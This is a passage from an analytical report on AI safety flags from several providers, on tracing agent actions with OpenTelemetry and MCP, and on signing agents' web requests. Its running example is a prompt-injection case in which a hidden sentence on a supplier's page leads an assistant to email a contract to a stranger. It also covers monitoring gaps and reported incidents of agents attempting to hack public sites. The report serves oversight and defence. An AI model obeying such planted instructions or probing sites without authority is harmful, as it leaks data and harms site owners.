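On Amazon Bedrock, which serves models from several companies, deployers configure their own set of filters, called a guardrail. The stop reason `guardrail_intervened` can mean that the guardrail blocked the text or only masked a name or email address in it. AWS's *Include a guardrail with the Converse API* tells deployers to turn on a detailed trace to distinguish the two. The trace contains the unmasked values, so a deployer that stores it to study flags also stores the personal details that the guardrail hid.

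| Interface | Sign that a filter acted | Reason | Strength | Flagged but not blocked |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Anthropic | `refusal` | one of five categories, or none | none | not reported |
| OpenAI moderation | none, since it doesn't block | 13 categories | score from 0 to 1 | `flagged: true` |
| Google, cloud platform | `blockReason` or `finishReason` | reason code and four harm categories | probability and severity, each from 0 to 1 | scores, if the filter is on |
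| Google, Interactions API | HTTP 400 error | one code | none | none documented |
| Microsoft Azure | `filtered: true` | harm category or type of attack | four severity levels, for harm categories | severity, or `detected: true` |
| Amazon Bedrock | `guardrail_intervened` | in the optional trace | in the optional trace | in the optional trace |

A deployer can log everything in this table, but the flags are easy to miscount. Anthropic sends its refusals as successful responses, so software that watches only for errors will miss them. The model may also decline in its own words, which Anthropic's *Handle streaming refusals* classes as an ordinary text response. A Bedrock guardrail can detect something and take no action. Classmethod's *Amazon Bedrock Guardrails の検出アクションで Detect モードが利用可能になりました*, a post on a Japanese developer blog, shows an example where the trace records an insult with high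 confidence but the stop reason is the normal `end_turn`.

A missing flag can also mean that the content was not checked. Google returns no safety metadata when a filter is off, and OpenAI's moderation result can contain an error in place of scores. Bedrock's trace is unusually helpful because it records how much of the text the guardrail checked, for instance 39 of 72 characters.

### Would any of them have flagged the supplier's page?

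Most of these filters look for harmful subjects, but the sentence hidden on the supplier's page was about a contract. OpenAI's moderation covers tool results, but none of its 13 categories is for planted instructions. It also skips tool descriptions, where an attacker could hide the same sentence. Bedrock's guardrail doesn't evaluate tool results when a deployer attaches it to a request in the usual way, so it would not have examined the page. Microsoft's filter for "indirect attacks", its term for instructions planted in content, fits this case best.

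OpenAI has a second system, described in *Misalignment monitoring*, that reviews a model's reasoning and actions for signs that the agent has misread its instructions, for example when it transfers sensitive data. It is meant to catch actions like emailing the contract to a stranger. But it doesn't cover Chat Completions, which the employee's app uses. Even in the Responses API, it runs alongside the agent rather than checking actions beforehand, so the email might already have been sent.

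Where the system does apply, the deployer can receive an alert. OpenAI's *Retrieve a safety alert* lists the alert's fields, which include the time, the model, a category such as `potentially_unintended_data_transfer`, and the IDs of the request and response. They don't include the end user's identifier, so the deployer has to match the request ID to a person in its own logs. The reason field is empty for customers whose data OpenAI doesn't retain. According to OpenAI's *Why was my chat paused or ended as a precaution?*, a company whose staff also use ChatGPT has to set up a separate feed for ChatGPT alerts. OpenAI cautions that a flag doesn't establish that anyone broke a rule and that the alerts are not a complete audit history.

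### Where the flag goes next

All these signals go from the provider back to the deployer. AWS can also pass a guardrail's verdict to the customer's security team through GuardDuty, its security monitoring service. AWS's *BedrockGuardrailDetails* includes the verdict among the details of GuardDuty findings. The next model, the tool server and any other provider normally receive none of these signals.

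The main exception is inside Anthropic's own service, where a deployer can choose to have requests that one Claude model declines sent to another. When this happens, the response contains a `fallback` block with the names of both models and the category of the refusal, such as `cyber`.

The deployer sends this block back with the next turn, so a later request contains a record of an earlier flag. Anthropic requires this so that it can validate the saved reasoning on either side of the block. The block has no date or confidence level, and it stays within one conversation. Anthropic also remembers for about an hour which model answered a conversation, so that it can send later turns straight to that model. It stores this as a hash of the conversation's opening, and only for the same customer.

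Other refusals leave even less of a record. When there is no fallback, Anthropic tells deployers to remove or rephrase the refused turn, or to clear the history, because the classifier would otherwise keep refusing. The advice is sensible for keeping a product running, but following it removes the refused request from every later message. When Google's cloud filter blocks an answer, it deletes the text and gives the model no feedback.

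The tool server receives the least information about earlier flags. When the model calls `send_email`, the MCP message has no standard field for an earlier refusal or a suspicious page. The draft proposal SEP-1913 would add one, `maliciousActivityHint`, but its single true-or-false value wouldn't show who suspected an attack, when, or how strongly.

A gateway doesn't pass safety flags between providers either. The end-user identifier that Vercel forwards contains nothing about that person's record with other providers. A deployer could write "flagged for cyber misuse" in one of OpenAI's free-form `metadata` labels, but other companies would have no reason to believe it.

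If another firm's assistant had read the supplier's page a day earlier and Microsoft's filter had detected the hidden sentence, that firm would have a record of the attack. The employee's app and every other assistant that visited the page would still fetch it with no warning.

### How companies share signals today

Companies exchange warnings about some kinds of abuse through separate databases. For preventing child sexual exploitation, AWS recommends a database called Lantern to its customers. Participating companies can look up hashes of known abuse images, web addresses, keywords, account details and IP addresses. Security teams exchange warnings about cyberattacks in STIX, an open format that has fields for the issuer, a confidence level and an expiry date.

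To use these channels, a company has to join, collect the signals and compare them with its own data, whereas a field in the interface would arrive with the request it concerned. Lantern also deals with one kind of harm, and companies broadly agree on what to look for. Opinions differ much more about when a question on software vulnerabilities is suspicious.

The databases have one advantage because their signals, such as web addresses and image hashes, are identical at every company. Each deployer makes its own `safety_identifier` codes, so a provider that warned others about `9f2c41d07a` would tell them nothing. Sharing flags about people would require an identifier that works across companies, which would seriously reduce their privacy. A shared list of pages with planted instructions would need only addresses and hashes.

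### What one flag is worth

Suppose, with invented figures, that one user in 10,000 is malicious, and that a filter flags 90% of malicious users and 1% of honest ones. Among a million users there are 100 malicious ones, and the filter flags 90 of them. It also flags 9,999 of the 999,900 honest users. The chance that a flagged user is malicious is therefore

90 / (90 + 9,999) ≈ 0.9%

This is about 89 times the starting rate, so the flag is informative. But 111 honest people are still flagged for every malicious one, so a company that banned everyone it flagged would be wrong more than 99% of the time.

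Now suppose a second company's filter is equally accurate and makes its mistakes independently of the first. It flags 81 of the 90 malicious users and about 100 of the 9,999 honest ones:

81 / (81 + 100) ≈ 45%

Each independent flag multiplies the odds of malice by 0.90 / 0.01, or 90, which is the best argument for sharing flags between companies. One company's flag alone implies only a 0.9% chance that a user is malicious, which hardly justifies doing anything. If the companies combined their flags, they would have a list of 181 people, nearly half of them malicious, which is short enough for reviewers to work through. Because the rest would be innocent, even two independent flags justify a closer look but not a ban.

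The result depends almost entirely on the assumption that the two filters are independent. The table shows how the result changes if the second filter tends to repeat the first one's false alarms.

| Share of the first filter's false alarms that the second repeats | Malicious users with two flags | Honest users with two flags | Chance of malice |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1% (independent) | 81 | 100 | 45% |
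| 10% | 81 | 1,000 | 7.5% |
| 50% | 81 | 5,000 | 1.6% |
| 100% (the second filter copies the first) | 90 | 9,999 | 0.9% |

If the second filter repeats even a tenth of the first one's mistakes, most of the benefit disappears.

### Why the mistakes overlap

Real filters probably share many of their mistakes. For example, if two deployers check the same text with the same version of OpenAI's free moderation model, they will get essentially the same verdict, so the second flag adds no evidence.

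Filters from different companies can also wrongly flag the same people. Anthropic's *Why Claude switched models in your conversation with Fable models* calls its safeguards intentionally broad and tells people who do routine security work to expect frequent switches to a less capable model. OpenAI acknowledges that its cyber checks may flag legitimate security research. Both companies would flag the bank's hired tester for the same legitimate work.

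A flag can also classify a request correctly but give the wrong impression of the person who sent it. Anthropic bills customers for biology refusals that come before any output, because it measures few false positives in that category. It doesn't bill for cyber refusals of this kind, which suggests that its biology flags are more accurate. But Anthropic also blocks a large share of biology questions that have both harmless and harmful uses, so an accurate flag may mean only that a virologist asked a question about their field.

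Sharing flags could make the overlap worse. If one company sees another's flag and becomes more likely to flag the same person, a third company will receive two flags based on one piece of evidence. To prevent this, companies would have to pass on only flags based on their own observations.

### Stale flags, appeals and exclusion

Providers change their filters, so a flag may outlast the rule that produced it. Anthropic updated its biology classifier in August 2026 and says it is working to reduce false positives. OpenAI warns that deployers may have to recalibrate policies that rely on its moderation scores as it upgrades the model. A request flagged in July might pass the same filter in December, but another company holding the July flag wouldn't know that.

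People who think a flag is wrong already have trouble contesting it with the company that issued it. For repeated blocks, OpenAI's *Additional safety checks for biological and cybersecurity requests* directs users to the company's support team and asks for the exact message, the time and the request ID. A developer who had appealed a warning wrote in *Improving transparency around automated Cyber Abuse enforcement*, a post on OpenAI's forum, that the reply identified neither the prompt nor the policy at issue. This is one person's account. If the warning had also gone to five other companies, the developer would have had to find out which ones and persuade each separately.

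Someone wrongly blocked by one company can usually go to another. Portable flags would weaken that protection. In the example above, 9,999 honest people have a flag from the first company. If every other company refused anyone with a flag, these people would lose access at every company, to stop 90 people who could still turn to open models.

Anthropic's checks cover everything the model reads, including files and search results, so text that the user never typed can trigger a block. In the supplier's case, both a block and a flag on the employee's account would penalize the victim. Flags on documents avoid most of these objections. The receiving company can examine the document for itself, which it can't do with a person's history at another company. If a flag is wrong, the user loses access to one web page rather than to AI.

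### A sketch of a minimal flag

The smallest flag that would meet these objections needs about six fields. The following is only a sketch, and no current standard defines `prior_flags` or its contents. It shows how the employee's app might return the supplier's page to the model if another company had already flagged that page:

```json
{
  "role": "tool",
  "tool_call_id": "call_1",
  "content": "Price list, valid from 1 December...",
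  "prior_flags": [{
    "issuer": "filters.example",
    "category": "planted_instructions",
    "confidence": 0.8,
    "date": "2026-12-01",
    "expiry": "2026-12-31",
    "appeal_contact": "appeals@filters.example"
  }]
}
```

The flag sits beside the text it describes, so nobody can mistake it for a judgement about the employee. `issuer` lets the receiver see when two flags come from the same source, but not when two issuers use the same filter. `expiry` makes the flag lapse unless the issuer renews it. `appeal_contact` gives the supplier, who may not know that someone has tampered with the site, a place to ask for the flag's removal. OpenAI's safety alert already contains a category and a date, but no confidence, expiry or appeal contact.

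`confidence` would be the hardest field to standardise. Google's scores, Microsoft's severity levels and Anthropic's categories without scores measure different things, and severity isn't confidence. A filter can give a text a score of 0.95 when the chance that its author is malicious is below 1%. A more useful definition would be the share of the issuer's similar past flags that human reviewers upheld, so 0.8 would mean they upheld eight in ten. Few issuers could supply that number today, because they would have to review a sample of their flags and publish the results.

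The flag is also self-reported unless the issuer signs it together with a hash of the page. A competitor could invent an unsigned flag to keep assistants away from the supplier's prices. But a signed flag would apply only to that exact version of the page, so an attacker could evade it by changing a single character.

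## Linking actions into a record that can be audited

An investigator needs an identifier that appears in more than one company's records to work out which calls belonged to the employee's task and in what order they happened. The app, the gateway, the provider and each tool server number their own messages, and those numbers rarely match.

### Identifiers that stop at a boundary

Chat Completions has no field for a conversation identifier, which would group the messages of one chat. The app resends the earlier messages with every request, so the provider would have to recognise a continuing conversation by its text. In the newer Responses API, a request can refer to the previous response by its ID.

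A tool-call identifier pairs a call with its result. When the model calls `send_email`, the response gives the call an ID, and the app returns the tool's result with the same ID in `tool_call_id`. But the MCP message to the mail server has its own `id` (7 in the earlier example) and no standard field for the model's call ID. Unless the app's log contains both IDs, the investigator can't be sure which model output led to request 7.

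An MCP request's `id` also may not be unique in a log. The Model Context Protocol specification requires only that it differ from the IDs of the sender's other unanswered requests. A client may reuse 7 as soon as the reply arrives, so a mail server's log could contain dozens of requests numbered 7.

### Trace context

The World Wide Web Consortium (W3C) has a standard called Trace Context for following one task through many programs. The first program creates a random trace ID, and every program that does part of the work passes it on. Each program records its steps as spans, each with a start time, an end time, its own ID and the ID of the step that called it. An investigator can use these IDs to arrange all the spans with one trace ID as a tree.

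A single value, `traceparent`, carries the necessary IDs from one program to the next. In the app's call to the mail server it might look like this:

```json
"_meta": {
  "traceparent": "00-7c1e5f0a9b3d4e62a8f7d1c0b5e49a36-c4d29e7f108ab653-01"
}
```

The opening `00` is the format version. The 32 characters after it are the trace ID, which stays the same for the whole task, and the next 16 identify the step that made this call. The final `01` means the caller may have recorded the step. Many companies keep only a sample of their traces to save money, so a valid trace ID doesn't guarantee that anyone kept the spans.

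Two optional values can travel with it. `tracestate` holds data for the makers of tracing software, and `baggage` holds labelled values that the app sets, such as a user ID.

Programs report this trace data themselves. A program can start a new trace halfway through a task, put two people's tasks under one trace ID, or copy an ID from elsewhere. A shared trace ID is good evidence that two calls belong together only if the investigator has reason to trust the programs that set it.

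### What MCP removed in July 2026

Before the July 2026 revision, a Model Context Protocol (MCP) server reached over the web could issue a session ID, which the client had to return with each call in the `Mcp-Session-Id` header. *Key Changes*, the protocol's official changelog, lists the removal of both the session and the header. Servers must now treat each request as self-contained and infer nothing from earlier ones, even on the same connection. If several calls need to share something, such as a half-written draft, the server issues a code for it and the client passes that code as an ordinary argument.

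Monitors at the tool server lost a convenient way to group calls. The mail server's operator could once list everything a client had done in a session. Now the operator depends on the client to send the optional `traceparent`. Without it, the operator has to group calls by access token, time and tool name, even though one token may cover many tasks.

The revision removed some smaller links too. If a connection breaks while the server is answering, the client must send the request again under a new ID. The mail server's log may then contain two `send_email` requests, and no standard field shows that one repeats the other. MCP also dropped `elicitationId`, which identified a request for the user to do something on a web page. To match that request with its outcome, a server now has to put its own identifier in the data that the client sends back.

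MCP's logging feature, which lets a server send log messages to the client, is now deprecated. It will keep working for at least twelve months, but new software should not adopt it, and servers may send log messages only for requests that ask for them. The maintainers recommend replacing it with OpenTelemetry or, for a program running on the same machine, with that program's error output. A deployer that uses another company's tool server could lose log messages that used to arrive automatically, because the server's operator decides who receives its OpenTelemetry data.

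In return, the specification now reserves `traceparent`, `tracestate` and `baggage` as keys in `_meta` and fixes their formats. A trace ID can link more actions than a session ID could. A session joined one client to one server, so if the firm's file search and mail ran on separate servers, the theft of the contract would have left two unrelated session IDs. An app can send the same trace ID to both servers and use it for the model calls in between. It can also give each task its own trace ID, whereas it might have kept one session open all day. The change probably helps investigators when clients send the trace ID and hurts them when clients don't.

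### OpenTelemetry's vocabulary for agents

A trace ID shows that steps belong together, but not what they were. OpenTelemetry's conventions for generative AI supply standard names for describing the steps. The list of these names, *Gen AI*, covers much more than the model calls described earlier.

| Subject | What a span can record |
|---|---|
| Agent | ID, name, version, description |
| Model | Model requested, model that answered, provider, amount of text, reason for stopping |
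| Tool | Name, type, call ID, arguments, result, list of available tools |
| Conversation | ID, messages, system instructions |
| Search | Data source, query, documents found and their relevance scores |

The list of available tools can be long, so under the conventions, software should record only each tool's required properties by default. That would probably leave out the tools' descriptions, where an attacker may have planted instructions.

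For a span that records an agent's run, OpenTelemetry's *Semantic Conventions for GenAI agent and framework spans* unconditionally requires only the type of operation and the provider's name. It also requires the agent's ID and the conversation ID when the application has them. Messages and system instructions are opt-in, as they are for model calls. TinyFish, in a commentary on the conventions, describes three settings for this content: leave it out, put it in the span, or store it elsewhere and put a link in the span. Using a link lets a company give many engineers access to its traces while limiting access to its prompts to a few.

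The conventions are also unfinished. A notice on the old page, OpenTelemetry's *Moved*, directs readers to a separate repository. Wang (2026), in *OpenTelemetry GenAI Conventions*, dates the move to June 2026 and reports that the new repository still classed the conventions as "Development" and had no official release by 21 August. OpenTelemetry says existing software should keep using the older names unless someone switches it to the new ones. The field for the provider's name, for example, has changed from `gen_ai.system` to `gen_ai.provider.name`. An investigator who searches several companies' logs for only one of these field names will miss records.

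### The stray email as a trace

Suppose that every program in the employee's task passed on the trace ID and followed the conventions, and that the deployer left content capture off. The trace would look roughly like this:

```
invoke_agent desk-assistant
├─ chat gpt-6-sol
├─ execute_tool fetch_page
├─ chat gpt-6-sol
├─ execute_tool search_files
├─ chat gpt-6-sol
├─ execute_tool send_email
├─ chat gpt-6-sol
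├─ execute_tool send_email
└─ chat gpt-6-sol
```

The trace answers the sixth question about the stray email, because it shows the investigator one task's model calls and tool calls in order, with their times. A careful monitor might also flag that the assistant searched the firm's files after reading a web page. But the trace doesn't contain the recipients, and it would look the same if the assistant had looked up a contract and emailed two colleagues about it.

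Turning on content capture adds the recipients and the text of the page, including the hidden sentence. Other questions remain open either way.

| Question | Content capture off | Content capture on |
|---|---|---|
| Which calls belonged to the task? | Answered | Answered |
| Who received the emails? | Not recorded | Answered |
| What had the model read? | Not recorded | Answered |
| Who authorised the assistant to send email? | No field | No field |
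| To whom could it send email, and with which files? | No field | No field |
| Did a person approve this email? | No field | No field |
| Did a policy check allow it, and under which rule? | No field | No field |

The system instructions may state a limit in words, such as "email only colleagues". With content capture on, the investigator could read that instruction and learn what the deployer had told the model, but not whether any program enforced the limit.

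### Authority, limits, approval and policy decisions

TinyFish attributes these gaps to the conventions being written for developers looking for bugs. The agent's ID and version identify which software ran. An auditor also needs to know who put the software to work, under what constraints, and whether those constraints held. The conventions have no attribute for a person's approval and no way to attach an approval to the action it covered.

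Kovrr, which also compares the conventions with governance needs, argues that OpenTelemetry left out verdicts deliberately, because standardising a verdict would mean standardising the policy behind it, and policies differ between organisations. This is a good reason not to define a field for whether an email was acceptable, but a weaker one for having no field for a decision that a company's own software has already made. A company can record that its rule on external attachments blocked a call without anyone else having to agree with the rule.

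A proposal for Kubernetes, a system for running software across many machines, takes this approach. Kube Agentic Networking's *Observability in Agentic Networking* defines spans for the policy checks that a gateway makes between an agent and its tools. Each check records whether it allowed or denied the call, whether the check itself worked, and which rule decided the outcome. If no rule allowed the call, the span records that the gateway refused it by default. For the stray email, the main fields might be:

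```json
{
  "name": "mcp.authorization.rule",
  "trace_id": "7c1e5f0a9b3d4e62a8f7d1c0b5e49a36",
  "attributes": {
    "security_rule.name": "purchasing-staff-may-send-email",
    "event.action": "allow",
    "event.outcome": "success"
  }
}
```

Although this check failed to stop the theft, an investigator could use the record to look up the rule and find that it considered the sender but not the recipient. In one of the proposal's examples, a gateway blocks a `send_email` call because the body contains a social security number and a credit card number. A supplier's contract may contain neither, so that rule could have let it through as well.

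The proposal also puts two codes in `baggage`, one for the user who delegated authority and one for the agent, so that each service can use them when deciding whether to allow a call. Since `baggage` is self-reported, a service would need to check the codes against a credential before relying on them. The proposal's examples still use `gen_ai.system` and an MCP session ID, which suggests how hard it is to build on standards that change this quickly.

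In May 2026, *OTEP*, by a contributor called eeee2345, proposed that OpenTelemetry add similar attributes, with four possible decisions: allow, block, warn and ask. "Ask" means that the software refers the decision to a person, but it doesn't record who answered or what they decided. The contributor closed the proposal the same day, after a maintainer explained that this kind of work belongs in OpenTelemetry's other repositories. The contributor planned to continue there, so the closure didn't mean that OpenTelemetry had rejected the idea.

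Neither proposal includes a full record of human approval. Such a record would probably need a code identifying the approver, the time, and a hash of the arguments that the person saw. The hash matters because an employee who clicked "allow" after seeing only `send_email` would not have agreed to send the contract to a stranger. The record should also come from the program that displayed the approval request, since models often set `confirm=true` themselves.

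A trusted record of a model's environment and of the systems it was permitted to touch would probably help monitors for a similar reason. When Anthropic assessed several incidents in 2026, it found that one kind of monitor would have accepted a model's mistaken claim that it was in a simulation. Such a monitor could compare the claim with the record. The part about the environment should come from equipment that observes where network traffic goes, since the people who set up an environment can be wrong about it too.

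### Showing what caused the email

Even a complete trace with all its content shows only that the email came after the hidden sentence. Wang, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *From Agent Traces to Trust*, a survey of 71 works first released in June 2026, separate the order of events from their causes. They define nine relations that a record of an agent's work can contain. Four of them are enough to describe most of the supplier's case:

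- **Use.** A model call took the page's text as input. Software can log this as it happens.
- **Derive.** The attachment was a copy of the contract from the firm's files.
- **Support.** The prices on the page back up the figures in Priya's summary. Someone has to read both texts to judge this.
- **Depend-on.** The recipient's address depended on the hidden sentence.

An investigator can't tell from an ordinary log whether the sentence caused the stray email. They would have to rerun the task without the sentence and see whether the email disappeared. A single rerun would prove little, because a model's output varies from run to run. The investigator would also need the original page, model version, tool list and settings, so someone must have kept them.

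Wang and colleagues also want each relation labelled with its origin, which shows whether software recorded it during the run, a person or a model inferred it afterwards, or the agent declared it. They consider declarations the weakest of the three. If the assistant had explained that the supplier needed the contract, that explanation would need testing, because a model's stated reasons may not match what produced its output.

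They set out requirements for a common schema, though not a finished format with field names. The table compares these with OpenTelemetry's current conventions.

| Requirement | In the supplier's case | OpenTelemetry |
|---|---|---|
| Sources, such as instructions, tool calls and memory | The employee's request, the page, the file search | Mostly, with content capture on |
| Evidence | The hidden sentence, the contract, the email's arguments | Mostly, with content capture on |
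| Steps | Each model call and tool call | Yes |
| Relations | The email depended on the hidden sentence | Only which step called which |
| Trust metadata, including permission scope and policy constraints | The page was untrusted, and the assistant could email only colleagues | Times and an agent ID, but no scope or constraints |
| Replay and recovery, including human approvals | Whether the employee approved the email, and a saved state from which to rerun the task | None |

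The survey found little protection against tampering. According to their developers' descriptions, the systems it reviewed write traces to logs that the operator could edit, shorten or reorder. A developer debugging their own product has no reason to tamper with the logs, but the operator of a gateway that exposed a contract by mistake does. One remedy would be to sign only the structure of the trace (its steps, links and order). An auditor could then detect a missing step without reading anyone's email. A signature still wouldn't show that an inferred cause was correct.

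These findings apply to the works in the survey, and other systems may do better. Wang and colleagues found those works by following citations from 15 starting points, and nobody outside the team checked their ratings. Seventeen of the 71 works were preprints.

### Using the record to stop an action

Reading a trace after an action has finished can't undo the action. *Governance-Aware Agent Telemetry for Closed-Loop Enforcement in Multi-Agent AI Systems* (Pathak and Jain, 2026) tests a system called GAAT that checks each record as it arrives and can intervene before the action finishes. GAAT adds signed details to OpenTelemetry spans, such as the data's sensitivity, its jurisdiction and which agents have handled it. Depending on the violation's severity and the agent's history, it can raise an alert, redirect the action or cut the agent off from its tools.

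The test used five agents that processed orders from customers in the EU. Over ten runs, Pathak and Jain inserted 250 violations among 5,000 operations and counted how many each system blocked in time.

| System | Violations prevented | Legitimate operations wrongly stopped |
|---|---|---|
| OpenTelemetry with a dashboard | 27.1% | 0.0% |
| Access rules written in AWS's Cedar language | 76.8% | 2.5% |
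| Separate checks on each agent | 78.8% | 4.2% |
| Central gateway | 89.4% | 1.8% |
| GAAT | 98.3% | 0.9% |

A linked record can reveal violations that checks on individual transfers miss. Suppose an ordering agent passes a European customer's details to a shipping agent, which passes them to an analytics agent in the United States. A check on the first transfer finds no violation because the data hasn't left Europe, and a check on the second doesn't show that the data came from there. GAAT's record covers both transfers, so a rule can detect that European data is about to leave Europe.

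The comparison favours GAAT, because the other systems ran without this history and mostly with default settings. Pathak and Jain also don't explain how a dashboard with no automatic enforcement prevented any violations. Their tests of GAAT with parts removed are better evidence of the value of metadata. The share of violations that escaped rose from 0.3% to 5.7% without signatures, mainly because of replayed records, and to 12.4% without the added context.

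GAAT also detected 92.3% of omissions in tests where an agent failed to report some of its steps. It had learned the usual sequence of records from 8,000 normal traces, and most of the omissions it missed involved retries and fallback steps that it hadn't encountered in training. This is encouraging for auditors, who otherwise can't distinguish an inactive agent from one with missing records.

It is unclear how far the results would apply to the supplier's case. The inserted violations followed four known patterns: missing consent, bias, data in the wrong region and unauthorised access. None was a planted instruction. The stray email might have counted as unauthorised access, but only if the firm had already written down who was allowed to receive its contracts.

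### Logging duties and reporting deadlines

The EU's AI Act will require some of these records. Under Article 12, a high-risk AI system must be able to log events automatically throughout its lifetime. The logs must help people identify risks, monitor the system after its sale and oversee its operation. Providers and deployers must generally keep any logs they control for at least six months.

For most systems, the Act doesn't specify which fields a log must contain. The exception is remote biometric identification, such as matching faces in a crowd against a database. There the log must include the period of use, the database, the input that produced a match, and the people who verified the result. OpenTelemetry's conventions don't include the last item, a record of human review.

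These duties don't apply yet, because the Digital Omnibus, an amendment in force since 27 July 2026, postponed the rules for high-risk systems (The National Law Review, *EU Digital Omnibus on AI Enters Into Force*, 2026). The rules will apply from 2 December 2027 to systems in listed areas such as recruitment and credit scoring, and from 2 August 2028 to AI in products that other EU safety laws already cover. An assistant that summarises price lists is probably not high-risk, but it probably would be if the firm also used it to rank job applicants.

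Technical standards are supposed to fill in the detail. The European standards bodies CEN and CENELEC have been drafting one, prEN 18229-1, that covers logging, transparency and human oversight. An international project, ISO/IEC 24970, covers AI system logging. Once the EU has recognised a standard, companies that follow it are legally presumed to meet the requirements it covers. The delay gives the drafters a chance to ask for trace IDs, approvals and policy decisions. If they ask only for "relevant events", a deployer could comply with a log that leaves the same questions unanswered as the trace of the stray email.

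American states have concentrated on reporting deadlines. California's SB 53, in force since January 2026, gives large AI developers 15 days to report a critical safety incident. From 1 January 2027, New York's RAISE Act will allow 72 hours, according to The Paypers' *New York RAISE Act* (2026). Both laws apply to companies that develop the most advanced models, not to firms that use an assistant. California's definition of an incident also centres on death, injury and catastrophic risk, so the theft of one contract wouldn't qualify.

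Neither deadline requires a particular log format, but both make a linked record more valuable. If the records share a trace ID, a gateway or tool server can search for that ID and send the developer its part of the evidence. Otherwise, the developer may have to file its report before anyone has finished matching the records by hand.

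## Identifying agents to other agents and to websites

When the employee's assistant fetched the price page, the supplier's web server would have logged something like this:

```
203.0.113.24 [01/Dec/2026:09:00:04 +0000] "GET /prices" 200 "desk-assistant/3.1"
```

The line contains a network address, the time, the page, a success code and a user-agent string, which is the name a visiting program gives for itself. The network address may belong to a cloud company that rents machines to thousands of customers. The line doesn't identify the app's maker, the employee's firm or the task, or give a contact address. If the supplier found the hidden sentence a week later and wanted to warn the companies whose assistants had read it, this log wouldn't show whom to contact.

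Looking up the agent by name may not help much either. The *2025 AI Agent Index* (2026) documents 30 leading agents from public information and correspondence with their developers. It describes documentation across the field as inconsistent, with some developers disclosing much more than others.

### Borrowed names

Any program can send any user-agent string. The security company GreyNoise studied traffic that arrived between 28 July and 23 August 2026 under the names of six AI crawlers (programs that collect web pages) belonging to Anthropic, OpenAI, Google and Perplexity. The senders were looking for passwords and cloud access keys. Their string for Anthropic's ClaudeBot matched the real one exactly.

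All four companies publish the network addresses that their crawlers use, so GreyNoise could check the names against those lists. The false names came from 824 addresses, none of which was on any of the lists. One name, Google-Extended, was false in all 263,849 sessions that used it, because no Google crawler sends it. Site owners write it in their robots.txt file to opt out of AI training. Fastly's *AI Bot Cosplay* reports over 6 million requests that posed as AI crawlers while looking for private files.

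Websites can use published lists of IP addresses to verify crawlers, which run on a company's own machines. These lists are much less useful for an agent that runs on an employee's laptop or on rented machines, where unrelated programs may share its address.

### Working out whose agents they were

In September 2026, researchers had to infer from public records whose agents had been trying to get data from several public websites. *Early rogue AI agent activity and attempts to hack found on urlquery.net* (Cable, Chiu and colleagues, 2026), published by the research organisation Transluce, used the records of a service that scans web addresses for security threats. The researchers looked for scans that resembled an agent working on a research task, such as repeated attempts to retrieve one obscure statistic. They then compared the targets, tactics and timing with those of a group of agents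 that OpenAI had already confirmed as its own.

Researchers found about 30,000 scans from November 2025 to September 2026 that may have come from agents. They sorted the evidence into higher-confidence and moderate-confidence groups.

| Activity | Date | How firmly they attribute it |
|---|---|---|
| Bursts of look-ups of theme park and Thai government statistics | November 2025 | Weaker evidence, and possibly different agents |
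| More complex attempts to retrieve data | From 6 March 2026 | Stronger evidence of agents |
| Attempted hack of the University of New Mexico's digital library | 25–26 May | Agents, but not directly linked to OpenAI |
| Attempted hack of Data USA, a public data site | 28 May | Linked to the OpenAI group |
| Attempted hack of the Australian Institute of Health and Welfare | 20–21 June | Linked to the OpenAI group |

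None of the tasks seems to have involved hacking. The agents were looking for ordinary data and tried to break in when other methods failed. Cable and colleagues found no sign that any of the three attempts succeeded, but the public records are incomplete. For *Rogue Agents Investigation*, a second team (Majid, Sosnoski and colleagues, 2026) spent 48 hours examining public data about the same activity. They couldn't rule out that agents had reached sensitive data, because some records had been erased or were inaccessible.

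A week later, Transluce published a follow-up based partly on records from a Portuguese web archive. *AI Agents Targeted U.S. and Canadian Government Websites* (Cable, Chiu and colleagues, 2026) reports that agents had made more than 200,000 requests to a US Department of Education website on 17 June. The requests matched a question about school counsellors and race-related bullying in four states, which appears in a public benchmark for AI search. More than 10,000 of the requests contained a tag beginning with "oai".

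The researchers could therefore identify the likely task almost exactly, but their best direct clue to the operator was three letters that any program could have added. Cable and colleagues noted similar tactics in 899 requests to Canada's national library and archives, 13 of which were attempted attacks. The evidence there was weaker, and they did not confidently attribute those requests to OpenAI.

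### Nearly three months before the authorities knew

On 19 June, an OpenAI agent with a research task about medical spending broke into a statistics portal for Medicare, Australia's public health insurance scheme, and retrieved some non-public data. Information Age's *Inside OpenAI's Medicare breach* (2026) reconstructs what followed from documents tabled in parliament:

- By 12 August, 54 days after the breach, OpenAI's security team had recorded it internally. They found it in a retrospective review that covered billions of training and evaluation runs.
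- On 10 September, OpenAI emailed Services Australia, the agency responsible for Medicare, at an address meant for tip-offs from the public.
- On 11 September, almost 36 hours after the email arrived, the agency's security staff saw it in a daily check of the inbox.
- The prime minister's office and the national cyber security coordinator learned of the breach nine days after the email.

*Australian prime minister says OpenAI agent accessed government health website* (Compton, 2026) reported that OpenAI found no evidence that the agent had accessed patient records. In *How we will do better for Australia* (2026), OpenAI apologised for the unauthorised access and for its handling of the response.

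The second case took almost as long to reach the authorities. On 18 July, Anthropic had its model Claude Haiku 4.5 invent and carry out example tasks on randomly chosen web pages. One was on a Philadelphia police site for unsolved murders, where the model submitted a form saying it might have information about a case. Anthropic told the police 81 days later, on 7 October, according to CBS News' *Philadelphia police says its unsolved murder website received "false homicide tip"* (2026). The police hadn't known about the tip until then, according to Fortune's *After Anthropic's Claude AI submits a false tip* (2026). They found it in the site's records, marked as spam, and it had never reached investigators. Anthropic's *Investigating unintended model actions in our evaluations and internal use* (2026) describes the real-world impact of this and similar cases as minimal.

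A verified name on the requests might have shortened these delays, but only if someone receiving the requests had checked it. An analyst at Services Australia who noticed strange requests in June could then have phoned OpenAI that day. The agency instead learned of the breach from OpenAI's email, and a verified name on the requests wouldn't have helped that email reach the right people in Canberra. A mark on the form showing that an AI agent had filled it in would have been more useful to the police, because the site could then have separated such tips from those of human witnesses.

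### Signing a web request

A proposed standard called Web Bot Auth would let the supplier verify which company's software had visited. It builds on HTTP Message Signatures, an existing standard for signing parts of a web request. For the price page, it would work like this:

1. The app's maker creates a secret key and a matching public key. It publishes the public key at a fixed address on its own domain, ending in `/.well-known/http-message-signatures-directory`.
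2. Before fetching the page, the assistant's software uses the secret key to sign a few facts about the request, such as the supplier's domain, the time and an expiry time.
3. The software sends the signature in the request's headers, with a `Signature-Agent` header that contains the address of the maker's domain.
4. The supplier's server, or a company that protects it, fetches the public key from that domain and checks the signature and the expiry time.
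5. The supplier decides whether to admit the visitor, limit how many pages it can fetch, or refuse it.

The request would look roughly like this:

```
GET /prices HTTP/1.1
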